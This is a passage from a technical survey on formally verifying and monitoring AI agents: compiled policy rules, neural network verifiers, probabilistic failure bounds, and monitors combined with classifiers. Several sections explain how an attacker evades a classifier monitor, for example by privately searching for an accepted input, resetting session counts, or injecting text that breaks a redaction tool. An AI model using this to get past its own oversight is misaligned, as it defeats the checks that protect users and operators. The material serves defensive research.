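A manager who can't read a formula can still judge a concrete case, so a solver can help by producing the right cases. Suppose two people translate the refund sentence independently. Let *h* be the amount already refunded on an order and *x* the new refund. One translation requires approval if *x* > 500, the other if *h* + *x* > 500. The solver looks for a case in which they disagree, which means

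*x* ≤ 500 < *h* + *x*

and might return *h* = 450 and *x* = 450. The manager then has to answer an easy question: may the agent pay another $450 on an order that has already had $450 back? The answer settles the ambiguity without anyone having noticed it beforehand. Of all the remedies, this one seems the most useful for the effort, but the solver can only find a difference if the translators read the sentence differently.

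Compiled and handwritten rules may well make the same mistake. Yu and colleagues compared their compiled airline rules with a handwritten set, which agreed with all 228 refusals. Yet at least four refusals in a sample were wrong. The policy forbids changing the flights of a basic-economy booking but permits changing the cabin. One tool makes both kinds of change, and both sets of rules blocked it entirely.

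They discovered this after asking a third reader, Claude Sonnet 4.5, about individual refusals. In a separate audit of 160 calls, the model agreed with the handwritten rules only about half the time. Yu and colleagues examined 77 disagreements and found that 30 were the model's own errors, 43 came from wording that can be read two ways, 3 exposed gaps in the handwritten rules, and 1 remained unresolved. The model makes too many errors to be given the decision, but its disagreements led people to the sentences that needed attention. Closing the gaps also raised the measured violation rate for the retailer with the gate from 3.3% to 6.9%, so the handwritten rules had missed about half of the remaining violations.

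In a mutation test, an engineer deliberately damages the rule, for instance by changing 500 to 5,000 or removing the need for approval, and checks whether any decision in a set of examples changes. If deleting the whole rule changes nothing, either the rule never applies or the examples don't cover it. The researchers who verified PocketFlow and libsignal applied the same idea to their proofs. The method takes little effort and is good at catching rules that have no effect, but it can't find a case that nobody considered. If none of the shop's examples contains a split refund, the rule that covers only single payments will pass.

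People still make the final decision, and how well they make it depends on what they have to read. Few managers could review the 600 lines of solver input for the airline policy. Ten rules, each next to its source sentence, are manageable, and so are a few dozen concrete cases, each with the decision the rule would produce. *Tether* refined its policy in a similar way, by looking at which recorded runs the policy blocked.

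Whoever settles the questions raised by the solver's output should also correct the handbook, because otherwise staff and agents will follow different rules. The shop's sentence might become "a refund that brings the total for an order above 500 dollars needs an approval that a manager has recorded in the refund system". This is clumsier than the original, but a new employee could follow it, and an engineer could translate it into a formal rule without guessing what counts as a refund or an approval.

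## Properties that depend on what text means

The corrected refund rule works because managers leave a record that the harness can read. The same handbook probably has a rule like "never mislead a customer". If the shop's agent has a tool that sends emails, the harness can compare the recipient with a list, check the labels of the data in the text and count the emails sent so far. These checks can't determine whether "your parcel left our warehouse yesterday" is true, because the call would have the same form, recipient and labels if the parcel had left today.

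Changes to code raise a similar problem. A policy can let a coding agent edit only `refunds.py`, but replacing `>` with `>=` in that file may fix a mistake or introduce one, depending on what the shop means by "over 500 dollars". Even with an exact definition of harm, Rice's theorem rules out a general procedure that recognises every harmful program. Cases that require inspecting the content are common, making up 22% to 28% of the replayable runs outside Tether's scope.

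Whether a payment is what the owner wanted is even harder to determine. Suppose the paper supplier cancels an invoice by telephone. The harness has the same invoice, purchase order and request that it would have if nobody had called. A monitor computes its decision from what it can read, so it treats both cases alike and gets one of them wrong. This applies to a language model acting as a monitor as well as to a Cedar policy.

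A narrower tool sometimes removes the problem. If the agent can only choose an email template, and ordinary code fills in the date from the warehouse's records, the email is as accurate as the records. If the agent writes free text, something has to judge what the text means, usually another neural network. Moon and Varshney's containment proofs don't cover such judgments.

### What verifiers can prove about a neural network

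A verifier for neural networks treats the network as a function *f* and tries to prove that

∀*x* ∈ *X*. ψ(*f*(*x*))

where *X* is a set of inputs and ψ is a property of the output. Vorobyov and Ilyushin (2026), in *Scaling Neural Network Verification with Tensor Parallelism and Fully Sharded Data Parallelism*, explain that in the most widely studied case, *X* contains every input within a small distance of one example. The property ψ is then that the network gives the correct label.

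The leading verifiers calculate a range for each neuron, layer by layer. Suppose *x*₁ and *x*₂ lie between −1 and 1, and one layer computes *y*₁ = *x*₁ + *x*₂ and *y*₂ = *x*₁ − *x*₂. Both lie between −2 and 2. If the next layer adds them, these ranges alone allow anything from −4 to 4, but the sum is 2*x*₁, which stays between −2 and 2. Better verifiers therefore keep formulas in terms of the original inputs. If the final range is still too wide, they split the problem into cases and repeat the calculation for each.

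For networks built from ReLU neurons, which output either zero or their input, the problem is NP-complete. In the worst case, the number of cases grows exponentially with the size of the network. Vorobyov and Ilyushin also note that the matrices must fit in a graphics processor's memory, which limits the size of the networks that standard tools can handle.

The field's annual competition shows roughly how far these methods reach. *The 7th International Verification of Neural Networks Competition (VNN-COMP 2026)* (Ladner, Kaulen et al., 2026) reports that the winning tool solved 3,164 of the 3,373 problems in the main track. The largest network, an image classifier, had 138 million parameters, and its problems concerned small changes to the images' pixels. The two vision transformers, which share their basic architecture with language models, had only 68,000 to 76,000 parameters.

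Only one benchmark involved language. A separate model turns each sentence into a list of 30 numbers, and a classifier with about 4,000 parameters sorts these lists into two classes. The verifier tries to prove that the classifier gives the right answer everywhere in a box around a sentence's known paraphrases. The proof doesn't cover the model that produces the numbers, so a new paraphrase can fall outside the box.

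Results for actual language models are narrower. *Certified Mechanistic Interpretability* (2026) applies such methods to GPT-2, an old model with 124 million parameters. It certifies the predicted next token for 20 of 50 inputs, if the numbers that represent the input change by no more than 0.002. Even this relies on a safety factor that the researchers chose by testing. *Towards Verifiable Transformers* (2026) describes a solver-checked result at the same scale, but it covers only how to close a quotation and applies to a specially constructed component, not GPT-2's own mechanism.

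Verification is currently practical only up to roughly 100 million parameters, and near that size it covers only tiny changes to single inputs. The models that run agents are far larger. Checking every possible text isn't feasible either. *From Transformers to Weighted Automata* (2026) notes that the number of texts grows exponentially with their length, and that a verifier without access to a model's internals may have to try them all. GPT-2's vocabulary of 50,257 tokens (words or parts of words) allows about 10⁹⁴ texts of 20 tokens.

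Faster verifiers would not supply the missing ψ, the formal statement of the property to be proved. One competition benchmark concerns networks that advise aircraft how to turn to avoid a collision. Their five inputs describe the state of the aircraft, so engineers can define which advice is acceptable in which situation, but nobody has a comparable definition of a truthful email.

### Bounding how often a model fails

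A weaker but more attainable goal is to bound how often a model's responses fail some check. Wadhwa, Suresh and colleagues (2025), in *BEAVER*, do this for one prompt at a time. A language model assigns a probability to every possible next token, so the probability of a whole response is the product of the probabilities of its tokens. BEAVER builds a tree of possible responses and always extends the most probable unfinished one. A fixed program, called the oracle, accepts or rejects each finished response. If *P* is the probability that the model gives an acceptable response, then at every stage

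total probability of accepted responses ≤ *P* ≤ 1 − total probability of rejected responses

If the accepted responses found so far have a total probability of 0.60 and the rejected ones 0.25, *P* lies between 0.60 and 0.75, because BEAVER has not yet examined the responses that make up the remaining 0.15. BEAVER does not use sampling, so the bounds for the prompt are certain if the oracle's verdicts are taken as correct.

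Wadhwa and colleagues tested five models with 4 to 70 billion parameters, using 300 mostly adversarial prompts per task. They called a prompt risky if *P* was below 90%. On a test for toxic language, BEAVER proved that 279 prompts were risky for Llama-3.3-70B and one was safe, leaving 20 undecided. Drawing random responses with the same amount of computation identified only 34 as risky. BEAVER can handle a model about 500 times as large as the biggest network in the competition because it fixes the prompt and runs the model normally, following only the likely responses.

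Each prompt took about two minutes, but the responses were at most 16 or 32 tokens long, and longer responses take more time. The method also needs the model's exact probabilities, which commercial providers rarely reveal. For toxicity, the oracle was a classifier, so the proof covers the classifier's verdicts rather than toxicity itself. An exact oracle, such as one that rejects every payment above €500, avoids this weakness, but the harness could simply block those payments.

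BEAVER also produced some evidence against judging a model only by its written reasoning. Wadhwa and colleagues looked at cases where two reasoning models drafted code in their reasoning that passed a security check. In 22% of these cases for one model and 49% for the other, the final answer had more than a 10% chance of failing the same check.

#### From one prompt to many

An evaluator can estimate the failure rate across many prompts by drawing a random sample from a stated distribution and calculating a confidence interval. BEAVER and *Lumos* (2025), a specification language, both use the Clopper–Pearson interval, an exact method for proportions. For each of the five models in BEAVER's privacy task, at least 42% of the adversarial prompts (with 95% confidence) created a more than 10% chance that the model would reveal an email address from a leaked collection.

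If a system passes all *n* independent trials, the one-sided 95% upper bound on its failure rate is

1 − 0.05^(1/*n*) ≈ 3/*n*

It takes about 3,000 trials without a failure to show that the failure rate is below 0.1%, and about 3 million to show that it is below one in a million.

*How Catastrophic is Your LLM?* (Wang, Chaudhary and colleagues, 2025) extends this approach to conversations. Its framework, C3LLM, bounds the probability that a model gives a catastrophic response in a conversation drawn from a specified distribution. Testing a fixed list of attacks can't provide such a bound, because the list isn't a random sample from a distribution. Wang and colleagues certified that, under some of these distributions, the worst model they tested had at least a 70% probability of giving a catastrophic response.

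*C-SafeGen* (2026) instead gives an upper bound for a model combined with a guardrail that filters its output. The system estimates the bound from test data, and the bound holds with a chosen level of confidence. This is closer to what a firm would want before deploying an agent, but an attacker can invalidate this kind of bound.

### Why an attacker voids the upper bound

Suppose a classifier misses 1% of harmful actions, and its errors are independent. The chance that at least one of 200 harmful actions gets through is

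1 − 0.99²⁰⁰ ≈ 87%

If the errors are not independent, the chance of at least one error can be quite different. If the 200 actions are identical and the classifier always gives them the same verdict, the chance is only 1%. If the classifier's mistakes rarely coincide, the chance can rise to 100%.

The test shows that the classifier accepts at most 1% of harmful inputs drawn at random from the test distribution. This bound does not limit an attacker's success rate, because an attacker who finds one harmful input that the classifier accepts can use it every time and always succeed.

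If no input were more than *k* times as likely to come from the attacker as from *D*, the failure rate would be at most *k* × 1%. But nobody can hold an attacker to such a limit. An attacker with a copy of the classifier can try random inputs from *D* and will find one that passes after about 100 tries on average, assuming the miss rate is exactly 1%. The attacker can do this in private, so the first real attempt works. Adding known attacks to *D* makes the test more realistic, but the next attacker may write different ones.

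Lower bounds on risk don't have this weakness. An attacker can always draw prompts from the evaluator's distribution, so C3LLM's 70% figure means that an attacker able to hold such conversations can succeed at least that often. These methods are therefore better at showing that a model is unsafe than that it is safe.

### Combining uncertain facts with exact rules

An agent's policy may depend on several uncertain judgments. *Efficient and Sound Probabilistic Verification for AI Agents* (Solko-Breslin, Mudrakarta and colleagues, 2026) describes a monitor that calculates the highest probability that an action breaks the policy, given bounds on the probability of each fact the policy relies on. The monitor blocks the action if that probability exceeds a threshold. The policy rules are in Datalog, a language of simple "if" rules.

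In their example, an agent removes private details from file A, combines the result with file B and sends the combined file to an outside company. A classifier gives a 90% probability that A is sensitive and 20% that B is, and the redaction tool fails 10% of the time. The combined file is sensitive if

(A is sensitive **and** redaction fails) **or** B is sensitive

If the three facts are independent, the probability is 0.09 + 0.20 − 0.018 = 27.2%. But the redaction tool may fail on exactly the kind of data that A contains, so the first term can be as high as 0.10. If the tool never fails when B is sensitive, the total is 30%. A monitor that blocks at 30% would stop the email in this worst case but allow it under the assumption of independence. The difference can be much larger if an agent runs the same redaction tool twice. Assuming independence lowers the estimated failure rate from 10%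 to 1%, although the tool may well miss the same name both times.

An exact calculation has to consider all 2ⁿ combinations of true and false for *n* facts. Solko-Breslin and colleagues therefore keep only the probability of each fact and of each pair of facts. Every real distribution satisfies the constraints on these probabilities, but so do some sets of probabilities that no distribution could produce. Because the monitor takes the maximum over this larger set, it can overestimate the risk but never underestimate it.

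They tested the method on 574 recorded agent runs from two benchmarks, leaving out those too complex for an exact calculation. At thresholds of 20%, 50% and 80%, it blocked every action whose exact worst-case risk was too high. At least 98.3% of its blocks were correct by the same standard. Converting each uncertain fact to a yes or no beforehand missed up to 30% of the risky actions. The calculation took 0.2 to 0.3 seconds on average.

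These scores compare one calculation with another, using probabilities that the researchers generated at random. The experiment therefore shows that the approximation is accurate, but doesn't measure how many real leaks it would prevent. In long runs that merge many files, the bound can approach 100%, and the monitor would then block almost everything. The method also assumes that attackers can't influence when the tools fail. If an invoice can contain text that makes the redaction tool miss a password, both the 10% figure and the result are wrong.

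#### Predicting a violation before it happens

*ProbGuard* (Wang, Poskitt and colleagues, 2025) estimates how a run is likely to continue. It is the only system in the survey by Dantas and colleagues that treats safety as a matter of probability. It reduces each situation to a few yes-or-no facts and counts how often one situation followed another in earlier runs. One example is a household robot that must not leave the kitchen for more than ten minutes while the stove is on. When the stove was off and the robot was in the kitchen, the robot turned the stove on in 31 of 184 recorded steps, or 16.85%.

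These frequencies form a Markov chain, a model in which the next state depends only on the current one. If *p*(*s*, *s*′) is the probability of going from state *s* to *s*′, the probability of staying safe for another *k* steps from a safe state is

*h*ₖ(*s*) = Σ *p*(*s*, *s*′) *h*ₖ₋₁(*s*′)

where *h*₀ is 1 for safe states and every *h* is 0 for unsafe ones. ProbGuard intervenes when the probability of remaining safe falls below a threshold.

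In driving simulations, it warned up to 15.84 seconds ahead at a threshold that caused no false alarms. For household agents, prompting the model again after a warning reduced unsafe behaviour by 65% and preserved 80% of the original task completion. Stopping the agent instead reduced unsafe behaviour by 94% but lowered task completion further.

ProbGuard's estimate is useful against accidents that develop gradually, where a monitor that only blocks the last step may act too late. But the learned frequencies come from the agent's past behavior. An injected instruction can make the agent behave in ways the recordings don't contain, so the estimate provides no guarantee under the arbitrary-output assumption.

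### Checking a model's statements against formal rules

Amazon's Automated Reasoning checks compare a model's statements with formal rules. A language model first translates a company's policy into these rules for an SMT solver. *VERAFI* (2025) describes each rule as a formal expression paired with a version in ordinary language.

Suppose a shop accepts returns within 30 days, and its agent writes, "You bought the lamp 40 days ago, so you can return it." A translator might turn this into *days* = 40 and *returnable* = true. With the rule

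*returnable* ⇔ *days* ≤ 30

the solver finds a contradiction, and the shop can stop the message. As with the order date in AWS's refund policy, a false date can still satisfy the rule, so the shop has to take the date from its own records.

In *Prove It, Part 2*, Buliani, Chunawala and colleagues (2026) promote the approach for Amazon as offering "full coverage" at a fraction of the cost of manual checking. A solver covers every case that the formal rules describe, but it can't cover a sentence that the translator misread or left out, such as a vague promise to "sort something out" about the lamp.

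*Position* (2026) argues that translation by a language model is compatible with certainty if a sound checker makes the final decision, whereas a learned judge gives only probable answers. This is true for the formulas, but the guarantee for the original text is only as reliable as the translator, even though the solver makes no mistakes. People can check the translation of a theorem once and then rely on any proof of it, but a customer-service agent produces new sentences all day, and each one could be mistranslated.

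### A proved limit around a fallible judge

A classifier can still add protection to a proved monitor without weakening the proof. *LEANGUARD* (2026) describes a monitor of the kind needed for the proved part. It checks whether a tool call is permissible under a reviewed policy, given trusted facts and the calls made so far. Write Π(*s*, *a*) if such a monitor allows action *a* in state *s*, and *C*(*a*) if a classifier accepts the action. The harness then executes *a* only if

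Π(*s*, *a*) ∧ *C*(*a*)

The theorem about Π still holds however bad the classifier is, so the classifier can't make the agent break a proved rule. For these rules, a payment that the classifier blocks is no different from one that the model never proposed, and the proof already covers every sequence of proposals. The classifier's false alarms can still make the agent less useful.

The monitor also makes the classifier more effective by limiting the number of attempts. Suppose it ends a session after the classifier has blocked five payments. The agent can then propose at most five harmful payments before one gets through or the session ends. If the classifier has at most a 1% chance of missing each one, the chance that any gets through is at most 5%, whether or not the errors are independent. With 200 attempts, the same calculation gives 200%, which is not a useful bound. As with spending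 limits, an attacker who can start new sessions can reset the count unless it carries over between sessions.

For the bookkeeping agent, the combined guarantee has two parts:

- Whatever the model, the classifier and the attacker do, the agent pays at most €5,000 in a session, and only to accounts on the firm's list.
- If harmful payments resemble the cases used to test the classifier, the chance that any of them gets through in a session is at most 5%, provided the estimated miss rate is correct.

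The first part depends on complete mediation and the rest of the trusted base. The second also depends on the test distribution, so it covers the model's ordinary mistakes but not an attacker who has found an input the classifier misses.

If the classifier can approve a payment that the monitor would otherwise block, the theorem guarantees only that every payment either followed the rules or had the classifier's approval. An attacker who deceives the classifier can then get any payment through that it has the power to approve. A separate proved limit on approved payments would contain the damage, and the owner should set it at an amount the firm could afford to lose if the classifier approved every fraudulent payment.
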